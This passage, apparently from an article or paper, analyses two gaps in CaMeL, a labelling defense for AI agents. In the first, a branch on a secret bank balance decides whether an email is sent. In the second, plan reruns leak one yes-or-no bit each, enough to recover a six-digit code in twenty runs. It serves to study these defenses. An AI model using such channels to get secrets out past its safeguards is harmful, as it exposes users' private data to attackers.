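If the balance is $15,000, the third line sets `small` to false and the interpreter marks it as secret. The fourth line then does nothing, so `rich` stays true and keeps its public label, and the email goes out. If the balance is $5,000, no email goes out. The recipient can therefore tell whether the balance is above $10,000, even though no value marked as secret reached the email tool.

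The other gap is that CaMeL does not track labels in the code that reruns a plan after a failure. Whether the policy blocks a run can depend on a secret, so each run can reveal the answer to one yes-or-no question. Twenty answers can identify any six-digit code, because 2^20 is slightly more than a million. An attacker would need some influence over the program and a way to observe the outcome, so this attack is probably much harder than planting a false sentence in an email.

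Garby and colleagues closed the first gap by making every operation in their language pass on labels. Their guarantee, like almost all of this kind, does not cover what an observer can learn from whether a program finishes.
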